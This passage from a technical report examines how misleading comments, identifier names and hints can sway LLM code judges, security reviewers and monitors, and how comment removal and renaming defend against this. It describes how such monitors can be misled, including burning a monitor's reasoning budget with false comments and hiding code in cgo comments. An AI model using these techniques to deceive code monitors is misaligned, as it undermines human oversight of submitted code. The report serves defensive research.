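The study also covered three reasoning models (o3-mini, DeepSeek-R1 and QwQ-32B), which work through a problem at length before answering. They answered more than 93% of the baseline questions correctly. All the structural changes together lowered their accuracy by less than 2 points, and print statements lowered it by less than 4. Contradictory comments lowered o3-mini's accuracy by up to 12.3 points and that of the other two by at most 4.6.

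False hints about the result had a much larger effect on o3-mini. Its accuracy on LiveCodeBench fell from 99.0% to 79.3% at the low reasoning setting and from 100% to 71.6% at the high setting, so more reasoning made the model easier to mislead. DeepSeek-R1 and QwQ-32B lost at most 2.3 points, but they wrote two to three times as much before answering. In one case from Lam and colleagues' presentation, QwQ-32B found the correct answer, −1, then tried to reconcile it with a comment that gave the answer as 12, and eventually got stuck repeating itself. Similar runaway reasoning, more than 32,000 tokens (word fragments) long, occurred on 4 of the 479 LiveCodeBench questions.

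A monitor that reads thousands of submissions may have a limit on how long it can reason about each one. Someone submitting code could then use false comments to use up that time, even if the monitor would have reached the right verdict with more of it. The researchers did not test this attack, but deleting comments would prevent it.

### Revising code after a review

Changes that a basic normalizer leaves alone can matter more than changes to names. In *Consistent or Sensitive?*, Pirouzkhah, Serbout and Bacchelli (2026) studied models that revise code in response to a reviewer's comment. They took 2,032 Java methods from GitHub projects, each with a comment and the developer's own revision, and rewrote the methods in nine ways designed to preserve behaviour, such as swapping the two branches of an `if` statement and negating its condition. A model succeeded only if it reproduced the developer's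 revision exactly, apart from the same rewrite.

The five models were T5-small, a fine-tuned LLaMA-7B, LLaMA 3.3 70B, GPT-3.5 Turbo and DeepSeek-V3. For each model, the researchers looked only at methods it had revised successfully in their original form. In the worst case, the fine-tuned LLaMA-7B failed on 45.3% of these after a rewrite. Some failures might have occurred without the rewrite, because these models do not always give the same answer twice. Requiring an exact match with the developer's revision also rejects good revisions that are written differently.

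The study's tables are inconsistent on some results for the fine-tuned LLaMA-7B and DeepSeek-V3. For the other three models, replacing variable names with five random letters caused failures on 8–17% of the methods that all five models had originally handled, and swapping the branches caused failures on 20–41%. Rewrites hurt performance more when they affected the lines the reviewer had commented on. Asking for step-by-step reasoning did not solve the problem, and it made GPT-3.5 Turbo less consistent on average.

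This study measures revisions, so we can't infer from its percentages how often a judge would change its verdict. It does show that models can react strongly to structural changes that removing comments, renaming and reformatting would not undo.

### How old the evidence is

None of the models in these three studies is newer than early 2025. Most of Moon's judges date from 2024, and CodeLLaMA from 2023. The models available in late 2026 are much better at following code, so they may be harder to mislead, and the percentages above should not serve as estimates for current judges. But better reasoning may not be enough to keep a model from being misled, since o3-mini answered the baseline questions almost perfectly and still relied on false hints.

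Two more recent studies give related evidence, though neither repeats these experiments on the latest models. Barkhordar and Thapa ran their comparisons on newer models, including Claude Haiku 4.5, and still found a preference for documented code. *Bias in the Loop* (Zhao, Esmaeili and Fard, 2026) left the code unchanged and added cues to the judge's instructions. A GPT-based judge choosing the better of two sets of tests was right 77.5% of the time without a cue and 62.5% with a distracting one. Canonicalizing the code would not help there, because the cue is in the instructions.

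### Which step removes which change

None of the experiments varied layout alone, so they do not show how much printing code in a fixed layout affects a judge. Unused functions remain after all three basic steps, because a normalizer renames their variables and prints them like any other code. To delete one safely, a tool must confirm that no other code uses it, including code in other files and code that looks up functions by name at runtime.

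| Change | What removes it |
|---|---|
| Claims that the code is correct, or about who wrote it | Comment removal |
| Comments that misdescribe the code or its result | Comment and docstring removal |
| Long, random or misleading local names | Renaming |
| Misleading names that other files use | Renaming only if the tool can update every use |
| Unusual spacing, blank lines and redundant parentheses | Printing in a fixed layout |
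| Unused functions and branches that never run | An additional step that finds and deletes unused code |
| Swapped branches and roundabout conditions | Additional rules for rewriting control flow and expressions |
| Misleading print statements | No basic step, since printing is part of the program's behaviour |

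## Removing comments and docstrings

Removing comments is the simplest of the three steps, and in most files it does not change what the program does. It can go wrong if the tool mistakes other text for a comment, or if it deletes a comment or docstring that another program reads.

### Finding the comments

Searching for the characters that start a comment is not reliable. Here is a line of Python:

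```python
url = "https://example.org/#install"  # project page
```

If a URL string contains a `#`, a script that deletes everything from the first `#` onwards could leave `url = "https://example.org/`, with no closing quote. In JavaScript and Go, where comments start with `//`, the same method would leave `url = "https:`. These errors are easy to notice because the damaged file no longer runs. Multi-line strings are more dangerous. If a Python program builds a shell script in such a string, deleting every line that starts with `#` leaves valid Python that produces a different script.

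A tokenizer avoids this. It reads the file from left to right and divides it into tokens, which are the smallest meaningful units of the language, such as names, operators, strings and comments. After an opening quote, it treats everything up to the matching closing quote as part of one string. It divides the line above into a name, an equals sign, a string and a comment, and the tool then drops the comment.

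Some languages need something in the comment's place. In C, `int/* count */n` declares a variable called `n`, but without the comment it would read `intn`. Putting a space there solves that problem, but not the one in this JavaScript function:

```javascript
function total(a, b) {
    return /* add the
              two amounts */ a + b;
}
```

JavaScript treats a comment that contains a line break as a line break, and a line break straight after `return` ends the statement. A function with such a comment between `return` and a sum therefore returns `undefined`. If the canonicalizing tool replaced the comment with a space, the judge would see a function that returns the sum and would approve code that doesn't work. The tool has to leave a line break wherever the comment contained one.

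Parsing the file into a syntax tree and printing it again also handles all these cases, because the tree records how the parser interpreted the text. Working with tokens is useful when the reader needs the original layout, for example to refer to line numbers.

### Deleting docstrings

Parsing already drops the comments, so this function only has to find and delete the docstrings:

```python
import ast

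HAS_DOCSTRING = (ast.Module, ast.ClassDef,
                 ast.FunctionDef, ast.AsyncFunctionDef)

def is_plain_string(node):
    return (isinstance(node, ast.Expr)
            and isinstance(node.value, ast.Constant)
            and isinstance(node.value.value, str))

def strip(source):
    tree = ast.parse(source)
    for node in ast.walk(tree):
        if isinstance(node, HAS_DOCSTRING):
            while node.body and is_plain_string(node.body[0]):
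                del node.body[0]
            if not node.body and not isinstance(node, ast.Module):
                node.body.append(ast.Pass())
    return ast.unparse(tree)
```

`strip` visits every module, class and function and deletes any plain string at the start of its body. Python doesn't allow a class or function to have an empty body, so if the docstring was the only statement, `strip` adds `pass`, which does nothing.

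The `while` loop is needed because an author can write two strings in a row. Python treats only the first as the docstring, but once the tool deletes it, the second becomes the docstring. A tool that deleted only one string per pass would leave the second for the judge to read, and would not be idempotent.

The tool must also remove only plain strings as docstrings. A string with an `f` before the opening quote may look like a docstring at the top of a function, but it can contain expressions, including function calls, that Python evaluates when it reaches that line.

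### Comments that affect the build

Go, a compiled language from Google, puts many instructions to its tools in comments. Go's *Command compile* describes the usual form as `//go:` followed by a name, with no space after the slashes. Deleting these comments can change the program:

- `//go:build linux` limits a file to Linux builds, according to the Go wiki. Without it, the file may become part of the program on other systems as well. The position also matters. Go's *Bug-resistant build constraints* notes that only blank lines and other line comments may come before it.
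- `//go:embed hello.txt` fills the variable declared below it with the contents of that file at compile time, as Go's *embed* (2025) explains. Without the comment, a string variable declared this way would simply be empty, and the program could still compile.
- `//go:linkname` can connect a function's name to a function in another package, even one that the other package keeps private. A reader who doesn't see the comment can't tell which code a call will run.
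- `//go:nosplit` turns off a function's usual check for stack overflow. Outside low-level code, this can corrupt memory.

The most serious case is cgo, the tool that lets Go programs call C code. According to the cgo documentation (Go, 2009), a comment immediately before the line `import "C"` may contain any C code, including whole functions. If a normalizer deletes this comment, harmful code could run without the judge seeing it.

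The list of special comments also depends on the compiler. The Go compiler described in Sourceware's *Compiler Directives* accepts `//extern`, which sets the name that code outside the program uses for a function. `go generate` runs commands listed in source files without parsing those files. According to the documentation in a commit by Shuralyov, it therefore also acts on lines inside multiline strings that look like its instructions.

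Python has far fewer cases, mainly the encoding declaration at the top of a file. A normalizer can safely remove this line if it decodes the file with the declared encoding and saves the result as UTF-8, Python's default. Without this conversion, Python may reject the file or read some characters differently.

### Docstrings that programs read

Python's doctest module finds examples in docstrings, runs them and compares the results with the expected output. This docstring contains a claim and a test:

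```python
def double(n):
    """Checked on every possible input.

    >>> double(4)
    8
    """
    return n + n
```

Deleting the docstring doesn't change what `double` returns, but it removes the test. A later test run would report no failures because there was nothing to run. The normalizer can keep the example and delete the sentence above it. Removing comments inside examples can still change which tests run, because `# doctest: +SKIP` makes doctest skip a test.

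In other programs, docstrings affect the main behaviour. PLY, a Python library for building parsers, reads its grammar rules from the docstrings of functions whose names start with `p_`. If the tool deletes those docstrings, the judge can no longer see what input the program accepts. Searching the program for `__doc__` would not reveal this dependency, because the code that reads the docstrings is in the library.

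### What to keep

A safe rule is to delete a comment or docstring only if nothing that builds, tests or runs the code reads it. For comments, the normalizer needs a list of exceptions for each language and compiler, and it should leave any comment that matches the list in its original position. For docstrings, it needs to check whether the program or the libraries the program uses read them. If it can't tell, it should keep the docstring and mark it for the judge as an unverified statement by the author.

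Exceptions to comment removal should be listed by name, because a general pattern would let authors write comments that the normalizer doesn't remove. Developers on the Go issue tracker discussed recognizing instructions as two slashes, a word, a colon and a letter or digit, with no spaces. That pattern would miss the instruction `//extern` and keep a comment such as `//note:verified`, which only a human or model would read.

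Text that the normalizer must keep can still contain persuasion. The C code in a cgo comment may itself contain comments, so the normalizer should process it as C. Other tools may also read comments that the compiler ignores. For example, Bandit, which searches Python code for security problems, skips lines marked `# nosec` by default. A company that runs Bandit on untrusted code should turn this feature off or remove those comments first, because otherwise the code's author can hide lines from Bandit.

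### A test on security reviewers

Moon and colleagues found that short comments could change a model's verdict on whether code was correct. *LLM Code Reviewers Are Harder to Fool Than You Think* (Thornton, 2026) found no such effect when models looked for security vulnerabilities.

Thornton wrote 100 programs, mostly 15–60 lines long, in Python, JavaScript and Java. Each contained one known vulnerability, such as a database query that an attacker could alter. The executable code stayed the same while the comments varied in eight ways:

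- no comments
- accurate comments, including warnings about the vulnerability
- neutral descriptions that didn't mention security
- misleading descriptions of what the code did
- adversarial comments, which falsely claimed that someone had reviewed the code or that another system made it safe
- detailed records of invented security reviews
- long comments on the safe parts of the code and brief, dismissive ones on the vulnerable part
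- false technical arguments that cited real security standards

The last three versions covered only 30 of the programs. Thornton tested five commercial models and three open-source ones, but used only the uncommented and adversarial versions for the open-source models. The study included 14,012 evaluations, 4,646 of them to test defences.

The main comparison tested each model on the same programs with no comments and with adversarial comments. "Lost" is the number of vulnerabilities a model found only without the comments, and "gained" is the number it found only with them.

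| Model | Found without comments (%) | Found with adversarial comments (%) | Lost | Gained | p |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 95.0 | 94.0 | 1 | 0 | 1.000 |
| GPT-5.2 | 93.0 | 91.9 | 3 | 2 | 1.000 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 91.9 | 91.9 | 4 | 4 | 1.000 |
| DeepSeek Chat | 89.0 | 93.0 | 1 | 5 | 0.219 |
| Perplexity Sonar Pro | 96.1 | 92.0 | 5 | 2 | 0.453 |
| Llama 3.3 70B | 72.0 | 71.0 | 12 | 11 | 1.000 |
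| Qwen 2.5 72B | 70.0 | 72.0 | 10 | 12 | 0.832 |
| DeepSeek-Coder-V2 16B | 53.0 | 58.0 | 12 | 17 | 0.458 |

The p-values come from McNemar's exact test, which uses only the programs where the result changed. If comments made no difference, each change would be equally likely to be a gain or a loss. DeepSeek Chat had six changes, five of them gains. Chance alone would split six changes at least that unevenly 14 times in 64, so p is 0.219. Researchers usually call a difference significant only if p is below 0.05.

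The eight models together had 48 losses and 53 gains in 773 comparisons, so nothing suggests that the comments generally hid vulnerabilities. The tests for individual models are less conclusive because they could fail to detect a 5-point increase in missed vulnerabilities, which Thornton considers important in practice. Even five losses and no gains would give p = 0.063, which is not significant.

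Some comments may have worked on particular programs. Three models missed the vulnerability in one Java program when it had adversarial comments. When Thornton told the models to treat all comments as untrusted, the commercial models' losses fell from 14 to 4. But those models also had 13 gains with the standard prompt, so many of the 14 losses could have been chance.

### Whether removing comments hurts detection

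Thornton advises against removing comments, arguing that weaker models need the context. The evidence is that DeepSeek Chat found 93.0% of the vulnerabilities with adversarial comments present and 89.0% after the comments were removed. But removal improved detection for Claude Opus 4.6, from 94.0% to 96.9%, and for GPT-5.2, from 91.9% to 95.9%.

These comparisons are misleading because the two sets of figures seem to cover different mixes of programs. The percentages before removal come from one version of each of the 100 programs. The percentages after removal all fit 290 runs per model, which matches two versions of all 100 programs plus three versions of the 30-program subset. The total of 4,646 runs also works out to about 290 for each combination of the four models and four defences.

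The subset was easier for most models. Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.2 found every vulnerability in it when the comments were removed. On this reading, those 30 programs account for 30% of the runs before removal and 52% afterwards. That larger share would raise the detection rate even if removing the comments had no effect.

It's possible to correct for this. Once the comments are gone, every version of a program should be the same as the uncommented one. Each model's results on uncommented code therefore predict what it should score on the 290 runs:

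| Model | With adversarial comments (%) | After removal (%) | Predicted from uncommented code (%) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 94.0 | 96.9 | 96.6 |
| GPT-5.2 | 91.9 | 95.9 | 95.2 |
| DeepSeek Chat | 93.0 | 89.0 | 91.4 |
| Perplexity Sonar Pro | 92.0 | 91.0 | 95.2 |

The mix of programs accounts for most of the improvement in Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.2. DeepSeek Chat and Sonar Pro scored below their predictions, possibly because the models' answers varied between runs or because the removal tool didn't reproduce the uncommented files exactly. Losing helpful comments can't explain the lower scores, because the predictions were also based on code without comments. Sonar Pro's prediction is also less certain because technical errors left only 75 of the 100 programs in its main comparison.

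The paired comparison in the earlier table is a cleaner test because it uses the same programs with and without comments. For DeepSeek Chat it happens to give the same two figures, 89.0% without comments and 93.0% with them, and the difference is not significant.

Even a significant difference would not have shown that removing *helpful* comments does harm, because the comments in this comparison were adversarial and made false claims about safety. At most, they might have helped by accident, for example by naming the type of vulnerability they denied. Testing the claim would require removing the kind of comments honest programmers write. Thornton's neutral comments are the closest to these, since the accurate ones revealed the vulnerability.

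### Reading the code twice and adding hints

Another defence in the study keeps the comments but limits the harm they can do. The model reads each program once with comments and once without, and the system reports every vulnerability found in either reading. False comments can't hide anything that the model finds in the version without them, and true comments can still help when the model reads the version that includes them.

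The four models found 96.1% of the vulnerabilities this way, compared with 93.2% when they read only the version without comments. Some of that gain may come from having a second try, since a model can notice something on one reading that it missed on another. Thornton did not have the models read the same text twice, which would have shown how much. The method also requires twice as many readings and combines the false alarms from both. The study did not measure false alarms, because every program contained a vulnerability.

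Adding hints from static analysis tools, which look for problems in code without running it, produced the highest detection rate, 96.9%. A hint might name a possible database vulnerability and its line number, with an instruction to check whether it was real. DeepSeek Chat reached 96.6% with these hints. But Thornton had already confirmed that such tools could detect the vulnerability in every program, so the hints could point directly to the answer. In ordinary software, the tools miss some vulnerabilities and report others that don't exist.

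The fourth defence searched for suspicious comments and warned the model about them. It scored 95.1%, yet Thornton reports that it recovered none of the vulnerabilities the models had originally missed, while the hints recovered 47% and the double reading 35%. These recovery rates are hard to interpret because they are based on 57 original misses with adversarial comments, but the main results imply only 27 for the four models in the defence tests.

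### Why correctness judges were easier to sway

Thornton's results may differ from Moon's because Thornton tested some newer models, including Claude Opus 4.6 and GPT-5.2, in February 2026. But model age can't be the whole explanation. Llama 3.3 70B, which is about as old as most of Moon's judges, showed almost no change in Thornton's study, while its close relative LLaMA 3.1 70B was among the judges most affected by the "correct code" comment in Moon's.

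The tasks also differ. Many vulnerabilities have a recognizable form, such as a database query assembled from user input, which a model can spot regardless of any comment about it. To reject a wrong solution to a programming problem, a judge usually has to follow the logic and find a case where it fails. If it can't do that confidently, a comment may sway its verdict.

Moon's judges also had to approve or reject each program, and half of the programs were correct. Thornton's models listed the problems they found, and every program had a problem. Listing a doubtful problem could raise a model's score but never lower it, so a comment that made a model slightly less suspicious might not have changed the result.

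The scoring may have hidden some successful deceptions. Thornton counted a vulnerability as found if the response contained at least one keyword for it. If a comment said that SQL injection was impossible and the model agreed, the words "SQL injection" in its answer could count as a detection. Thornton argues that any scoring bias cancels out because the same keywords apply with and without comments. That is reasonable for unusual wording, which can occur in both cases, but false detections from repeating a comment can occur only when the code has comments.

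Thornton checked 74 responses by hand, including 14 to programs with the three more elaborate kinds of comment. One of those 14 only repeated the comment. With so few cases, the true rate of repetition could be from 0 to about 21%. A rate near the top of that range could hide a real effect on detection.

Finally, Thornton wrote the comments in advance and did not adapt them to any model. Wu and Nita-Rotaru (2026) found in *ALIBI* that comments adapted to a particular detector did make it miss vulnerabilities, and that filtering comments before the detector read the code substantially reduced the problem.

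## Renaming identifiers

Once a tool has removed the comments, names are the main place where an author can still describe the code in ordinary words. Renaming removes those words, but it is harder to do safely than removing comments because a name must still match all its other occurrences, some of which may be outside the file or even the program.

### From old names to new ones

The tool first works out which declaration each name refers to, because the same spelling can stand for different things:

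```python
total = 0

def add_up(values):
    total = 0
    for value in values:
        total += value
    return total
```

The two variables called `total` are unrelated. Python treats a name as local to a function if the function assigns to it anywhere, unless the function declares it `global` or `nonlocal`. If other files read the outer `total`, the tool must keep that name and rename only the one inside `add_up`. Search-and-replace would rename both, but Python's `symtable` module gives the scope of every name.

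Next, the tool renames each declaration in order of first appearance. It can number variables through the whole file or start again in each function. With continuous numbering, one extra variable near the top changes every later name, which makes two versions of a file hard to compare. Starting again avoids this, but then `v0` refers to a different variable in each function. Either way, a nested function that uses its parent's variables has to continue the parent's numbering.

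The tool then replaces every use of each declared name. Python's syntax tree stores most of these in name nodes, but in `except ValueError as error:`, the name `error` is a plain string attached to the exception handler. A tool that changes only name nodes would miss this string but rename the uses below it, so the program would crash the first time that exception occurred, yet still pass any tests that never trigger it.

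All the replacements also have to happen at the same time. Suppose a function's first variable is called `v1` and its second `v0`. Changing every `v1` to `v0`, and then every `v0` to `v1`, would merge both variables into `v1`.

### Capture

A new name can also collide with a name that the tool keeps. This is called capture, because a use that referred to one declaration now refers to another. Here is a faulty permission check:

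```python
v0 = "admin"

def may_delete(role):
    return v0 == "admin"
```

The function ignores `role` and compares the outer `v0` with `"admin"`, so it lets everyone delete. A careless tool keeps the outer `v0`, which other files might import, and gives the parameter the first name in its series:

```python
v0 = "admin"

def may_delete(v0):
    return v0 == "admin"
```

This version checks the role correctly, so a judge would approve it, but the machine would still run the original. An author who knew the naming scheme could cause this on purpose.

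To avoid capture, the tool lists all the names it will keep, including built-in ones, and skips them when it chooses new names. The parameter then becomes `v1`, and the judge can see that the function never uses it. The list must not include names the tool will replace. Otherwise, a parameter called `role` would become `v1` but one already called `v1` would become `v2`, so two programs that differ only in that name would get different normal forms.

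### When something else reads the name

Even a tool that follows these steps correctly can change what a program does. This one reads the size of a room from a JSON file, a common text format for data:

```python
import json

def area(width, height):
    return width * height

with open("room.json") as file:
    print(area(**json.load(file)))
```

If the file contains `{"width": 4, "height": 3}`, the two asterisks pass its entries as keyword arguments, which Python matches to parameters by name, and the program prints 12. If the tool renames the parameters to `v0` and `v1`, Python stops with an error because `area` no longer has a parameter called `width`. The tool could have updated a call such as `area(width=4, height=3)`, but here the names are in a data file.

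Renaming can make some functions fail without an error. Suppose the definition were `def area(width=1, height=1, **other)`, where `other` collects any keyword arguments that match no parameter. After renaming, `other` would collect both values from the file, the parameters would keep their defaults, and the program would print 1.

Names matter in similar ways elsewhere:

| What depends on the name | Example | Possible result of renaming |
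|---|---|---|
| Reflection, where a program looks up its own parts by name | `getattr(handler, "on_" + event, None)` | The lookup returns `None` and the program ignores the event |
| Serialized fields | A class that saves its fields to JSON under their own names | The program can no longer read its old files |
| Framework conventions | The testing tool pytest, which by default runs functions whose names start with `test` | The test never runs, so it never fails |
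| Exported interfaces | Another file that contains `from geometry import area` | The import fails |

None of this damages the software, because the machine still runs the original, but it can make the verdict wrong. A careful judge who saw `area(v0, v1)` beside a file that uses `width` and `height` would reject a correct program. A monitor that ran tests on the normal form would get failures that aren't in the original or miss some that are.

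### Which names to keep

The usual compromise is to rename local variables and keep public names, imported names and attributes. Local variables are the safest to rename because other code rarely refers to them. Attributes are difficult to rename in Python because variables have no fixed types. When a tool finds `x.total`, it often can't determine which class defines that `total`. In Java, a compiler can usually work this out from the declared types.

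Parameters are local variables that callers can also refer to by name. A tool can safely rename one if it has access to every call, or if the function accepts that argument only by position. Otherwise it should keep the name.

Even local names aren't always safe to change. The expression `"{width} by {height}".format(**locals())` looks up local variables by name, and `eval` can run code that mentions them. A cautious tool doesn't rename local variables in any function that uses such features. But an author can then add a pointless `eval` to keep a misleading name, so the tool should mark for the judge where it skipped renaming and why.

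An author can also exploit the function names that the compromise preserves. In the faulty `median` function, the author could move the copying into a helper called `sorted_copy`, which only calls `list`. If the tool kept the helper's name, the judge would read `v1 = sorted_copy(v0)`. A tool that has the whole program can rename such a helper after checking that nothing outside the program uses it.

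In *RealVul*, Cao, Liao and Shang (2024) chose a version of this compromise for finding security vulnerabilities in PHP, a language for web applications. They renamed variables to `var0`, `var1` and so on, because a variable's name doesn't show whether the variable holds dangerous data. They kept the names of programmer-defined functions, because these indicate what the functions do. They argue that replacing these names without losing that information would require analyzing each function and its calls.

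In untrusted code, a function's name is only the author's description of it. A function called `escape_html` might return its input unchanged, and the name is most likely to mislead a monitor that can't see the function's body.

Cao and colleagues trained five code models with and without normalization and compared their F1 scores, which combine the share of vulnerabilities found with the share of warnings that were right. Normalization helped in most cases, by up to 14.06 points, though one model did worse on unfamiliar projects. The normalization also removed strings the researchers considered irrelevant, so renaming may not explain the gain.

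*Robustness of AI Models in Software Vulnerability Detection* (Gonçalves, 2025) found that normalizing code just before a model classified it made the model harder to fool with changed names but less accurate overall. When the model was instead trained on manipulated examples, it was nearly as accurate on manipulated code as on clean code.

### Functions called good and bad

Names can also reveal the right answer. The Juliet test suite is a large collection of small programs for testing vulnerability detectors. A typical program contains both a vulnerable and a safe version of the same code, in functions with names like `bad()` and `good()`. A model could score well on these programs by reading only the names.

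*VulnLLM-R* (Nie, Li et al., 2025) therefore removed such clues from the programs before using them to train and test a vulnerability detector. In the Java programs, it replaced every class, method and variable name containing a revealing term, such as "good", "bad" or "cwe" (from the standard numbering of software weaknesses), with a random seven-character string. It also removed the comments and changed the text that the programs print.

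Changing the text a program prints alters its behaviour, which is acceptable in a training set but not in a normal form. A list of revealing words also works only if whoever writes it knows which words to expect. An untrusted author could write `checked` or `trusted` instead of `good`, so a normalizer for a judge should replace every name it safely can.

### Choosing a naming scheme

Numbered names such as `v0` and `v1` are short, and the same program always gets the same ones. Names based on a variable's role, such as `param0` or `loop0`, give the reader a little more information, which is reliable if the tool takes it from the structure of the code. Names based on types are riskier in Python, which doesn't check type annotations when a program runs. If an author annotates an ordinary list as `SortedList`, a tool that renames it `sorted_list0` passes the false claim on to the reader.

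Random strings carry no meaning, but the tool must generate the same strings each time for the same program. If they changed with each submission, an author could resubmit the program until one set of names happened to get it approved.

Another option is to shorten only long names. This addresses the name-length effect that Moon and colleagues found and keeps many helpful names. But it also keeps short misleading names such as `safe`, and programs that differ only in identifier names still get different normal forms. A language model could instead choose new descriptive names, but the judge would then depend on whether that model understood the code.

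The renaming scheme can bias a judge even when it treats every author alike. The length of the names can cause this bias. So can names like `v0`, which make code look obfuscated and might lead a monitor to rate all of it as more suspicious.

The closest existing comparison of naming schemes, *Robustness and Trade-offs for Code LLMs on Protected Code* (Wen, Guo and colleagues, 2026), had seven models translate Java functions into Python and ran tests on the translations. On average, 58.2% were correct when the Java code had names like `v0` and `v1`, and 56.6% when it had random names. With 164 problems per model, a gap that small could be due to chance. The researchers suggest that distinctive placeholders might help a model keep track of variables, but they did not test this.

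Names that are hard to tell apart are clearly a bad choice, as the next experiment shows.

### What models lose without names

In *When Names Disappear*, Le, Pham and colleagues (2025) measured how renaming identifiers affects models' ability to summarize code and predict its output. They tested GPT-4o, Qwen3-Coder 480B, DeepSeek V3 and Llama 4 Maverick on short contest solutions from LiveCodeBench and on programs from ClassEval, a benchmark of Python classes that resemble ordinary software.

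For summaries, GPT-4o compared each model's description with a reference and scored it out of 100:

| Model | ClassEval classes, original | ClassEval classes, renamed | LiveCodeBench, original | LiveCodeBench, renamed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 87.3 | 58.7 | 73.4 | 70.1 |
| Qwen3-Coder 480B | 87.2 | 72.1 | 87.7 | 82.1 |
| DeepSeek V3 | 87.7 | 76.7 | 83.6 | 78.4 |
| Llama 4 Maverick | 86.2 | 66.4 | 77.5 | 78.2 |

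In one example, GPT-4o recognized a class as the game Minesweeper from names such as `MinesweeperGame` and `check_won`. After the identifiers were renamed, it described updates to a grid line by line and never mentioned a game. Renaming removed less information from the contest solutions because their variable names had a median length of about two characters, compared with about eight in ClassEval. Many of the solutions also use well-known algorithms that a model can recognize by their structure.

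This loss matters for monitoring, because detecting code that doesn't belong may depend on knowing what the rest of the program is for. But Le, Pham and colleagues renamed classes and methods as well as variables. A normalizer that kept public names would leave `MinesweeperGame` and `check_won` in place, so it would presumably lose much less information.

Predicting output should not depend on names at all, because the behaviour stays the same. For this task, the researchers chose 37 ClassEval programs and 96 LiveCodeBench solutions with many branches, and tried four kinds of new names:

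- numbered placeholders, such as `class1`, `method1` and `var1`
- strings of characters that look alike
- words from an unrelated field, such as `adrenaline_fd`
- misleading names, such as `compute_max` for a function that adds numbers

The table shows the average percentage of correct predictions for the four models:

| Names | ClassEval | LiveCodeBench |
|---|---|---|
| Original | 85.1 | 90.4 |
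| Numbered placeholders | 81.4 | 83.5 |
| Look-alike strings | 75.8 | 76.3 |
| Words from another field | 83.3 | 81.1 |
| Misleading names | 81.1 | 87.2 |

Look-alike strings did the most harm, which suggests that much of the difficulty came from telling variables apart. Surprisingly, misleading names did no more harm than placeholders on ClassEval, and less on LiveCodeBench. The two ClassEval averages differ by only 0.3 points, and small differences on that benchmark mean little because one program is worth 2.7 points. The LiveCodeBench result comes from GPT-4o and Llama 4 Maverick; the other two models did slightly worse with misleading names than with placeholders.

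Placeholders also lowered some models' scores much more than others'. On LiveCodeBench, DeepSeek V3 lost 0.7 points and Llama 4 Maverick lost 14.9. Stronger models' scores do not always fall. When Wen and colleagues tested renaming and four other ways of altering code, GPT-4.1's share of correct translations fell from 92.9% to 90.0%, while Qwen3-Coder-30B's rose from 88.3% to 90.5%. However, a model can often translate a function line by line without working out its purpose.

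Even a strong model can need the names. In one of Wen's examples, GPT-4.1 got the loop condition wrong when translating a binary search whose variables `low`, `high` and `mid` had been renamed `a`, `b` and `c`. It translated the function correctly after a separate step restored the names.

### Names as keys to memorized answers

One explanation for the lower scores is that models had memorized the outputs of some benchmark programs during training. A model could then produce the answer from a familiar name without reasoning about the code, and renaming would remove that cue.

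To test this, Le, Pham and colleagues gave the programs new inputs that should produce different outputs, and counted how often a model still gave the old output. They left out programs with only a few possible outputs, such as true or false, because a match could easily be a coincidence. On LiveCodeBench, Llama 4 Maverick gave the old output 9 times with the original names, 5 times with look-alike strings and 3 times with misleading names. GPT-4o showed a similar pattern, but DeepSeek V3 never gave an old output on these programs.

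The numbers are small, but a wrong answer that exactly matches the old output is hard to explain except by memorization. The effect persisted after renaming, so some models probably also recognized the code's structure. Memorization can't explain every loss in the previous table. DeepSeek V3 lost 7.5 points on LiveCodeBench with look-alike strings but showed no sign of memorization there.

Losing this kind of help doesn't really hurt a judge, because a new program from an untrusted author has no memorized answer. For the same reason, the scores on original code overstate how well a model would follow such a program. Recognition could even be dangerous, since an author might take a well-known function, keep its name and change one line, hoping that the judge will recall the usual version instead of reading this one. None of these studies tested that attack, but it would work the same way as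 the old outputs.

### Misleading names and human readers

People reviewing code also have to predict what it does. *Do Machines Struggle Where Humans Do?* (Le, Nguyen and Nguyen, 2026) compared language models with 50 computer science students from an earlier experiment by Nguyen and colleagues. The students read short Python and JavaScript functions and predicted their output for a given input. Each of the 20 functions had several versions, including one with meaningless names and one with misleading names.

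The models answered the same questions under 21 different prompts, some of which restricted their reasoning. Five of the seven models were right less than a quarter of the time in every version, so their results reveal little about names. The table gives the percentage of correct answers for the students and the other two models:

| Reader | Original names | Meaningless names | Misleading names |
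|---|---|---|---|
| All students | 40.5 | 38.7 | 38.0 |
| Beginners | 34.2 | 26.7 | 26.3 |
| Intermediate students | 45.1 | 43.1 | 37.5 |
| Most experienced students | 40.5 | 44.0 | 55.6 |
| DeepSeek-R1-Distill-Qwen-7B | 63.8 | 64.2 | 51.8 |
| SmolLM3-3B | 45.0 | 44.0 | 34.2 |

Students as a whole did hardly worse with misleading names than with meaningless ones. The most experienced students even did best with misleading names, which Le, Nguyen and Nguyen take as a sign that they relied on the structure of the code. But the percentages for this group fit 11 correct answers out of 25 with meaningless names and 15 out of 27 with misleading ones, so few answers that the difference could easily be chance. Even the figures for all students appear to come from only 106 and 121 answers, too few to rule out a difference of 10 points in either direction.

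The two models' accuracy barely fell when the names became meaningless, but it fell about 10 to 12 points further when they became misleading. Most of DeepSeek's drop was in JavaScript, where its accuracy fell from 58% with meaningless names to 38% with misleading ones. In Python, it fell from 70% to 65%. Each language had only ten functions, so a few unusual ones could account for much of this.

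Misleading names did not reliably make models more confident in their mistakes. On a separate set of 50 programs, nine models' average confidence in their wrong answers was higher with misleading names than with meaningless ones for 24 programs and lower for 26. A monitor's confidence is therefore of little use for detecting that a name has misled it.

### When a false name is worse than no name

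A true name can help the reader and a false one can do harm, so the value of renaming depends on how many programs have misleading names. Let T be the reader's accuracy with true names, N with neutral names and F with false names, and let s be the share of programs with false names. Keeping the names gives an average accuracy of (1 − s)T + sF. When T is greater than F, this is better than renaming if

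s < (T − N) / (T − F).

For SmolLM3-3B, the limit is (45.0 − 44.0) / (45.0 − 34.2), or about 9%, so renaming the identifiers in every program would improve its accuracy if more than about 9% of the programs had misleading names. DeepSeek-R1-Distill-Qwen-7B did no worse with neutral names than with the originals. For the four larger models, it is better to keep the original names, because renaming would improve their accuracy on ClassEval only if more than 93% of the programs had misleading names, and would never improve it on LiveCodeBench.

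Larger models may be better at checking a name against the code, which would explain the difference, but the two experiments also used different programs and different misleading names. All of these models are older than those available in late 2026. The limits show how much the answer depends on the reader, so anyone deploying a judge would need to measure T, N and F for that judge.

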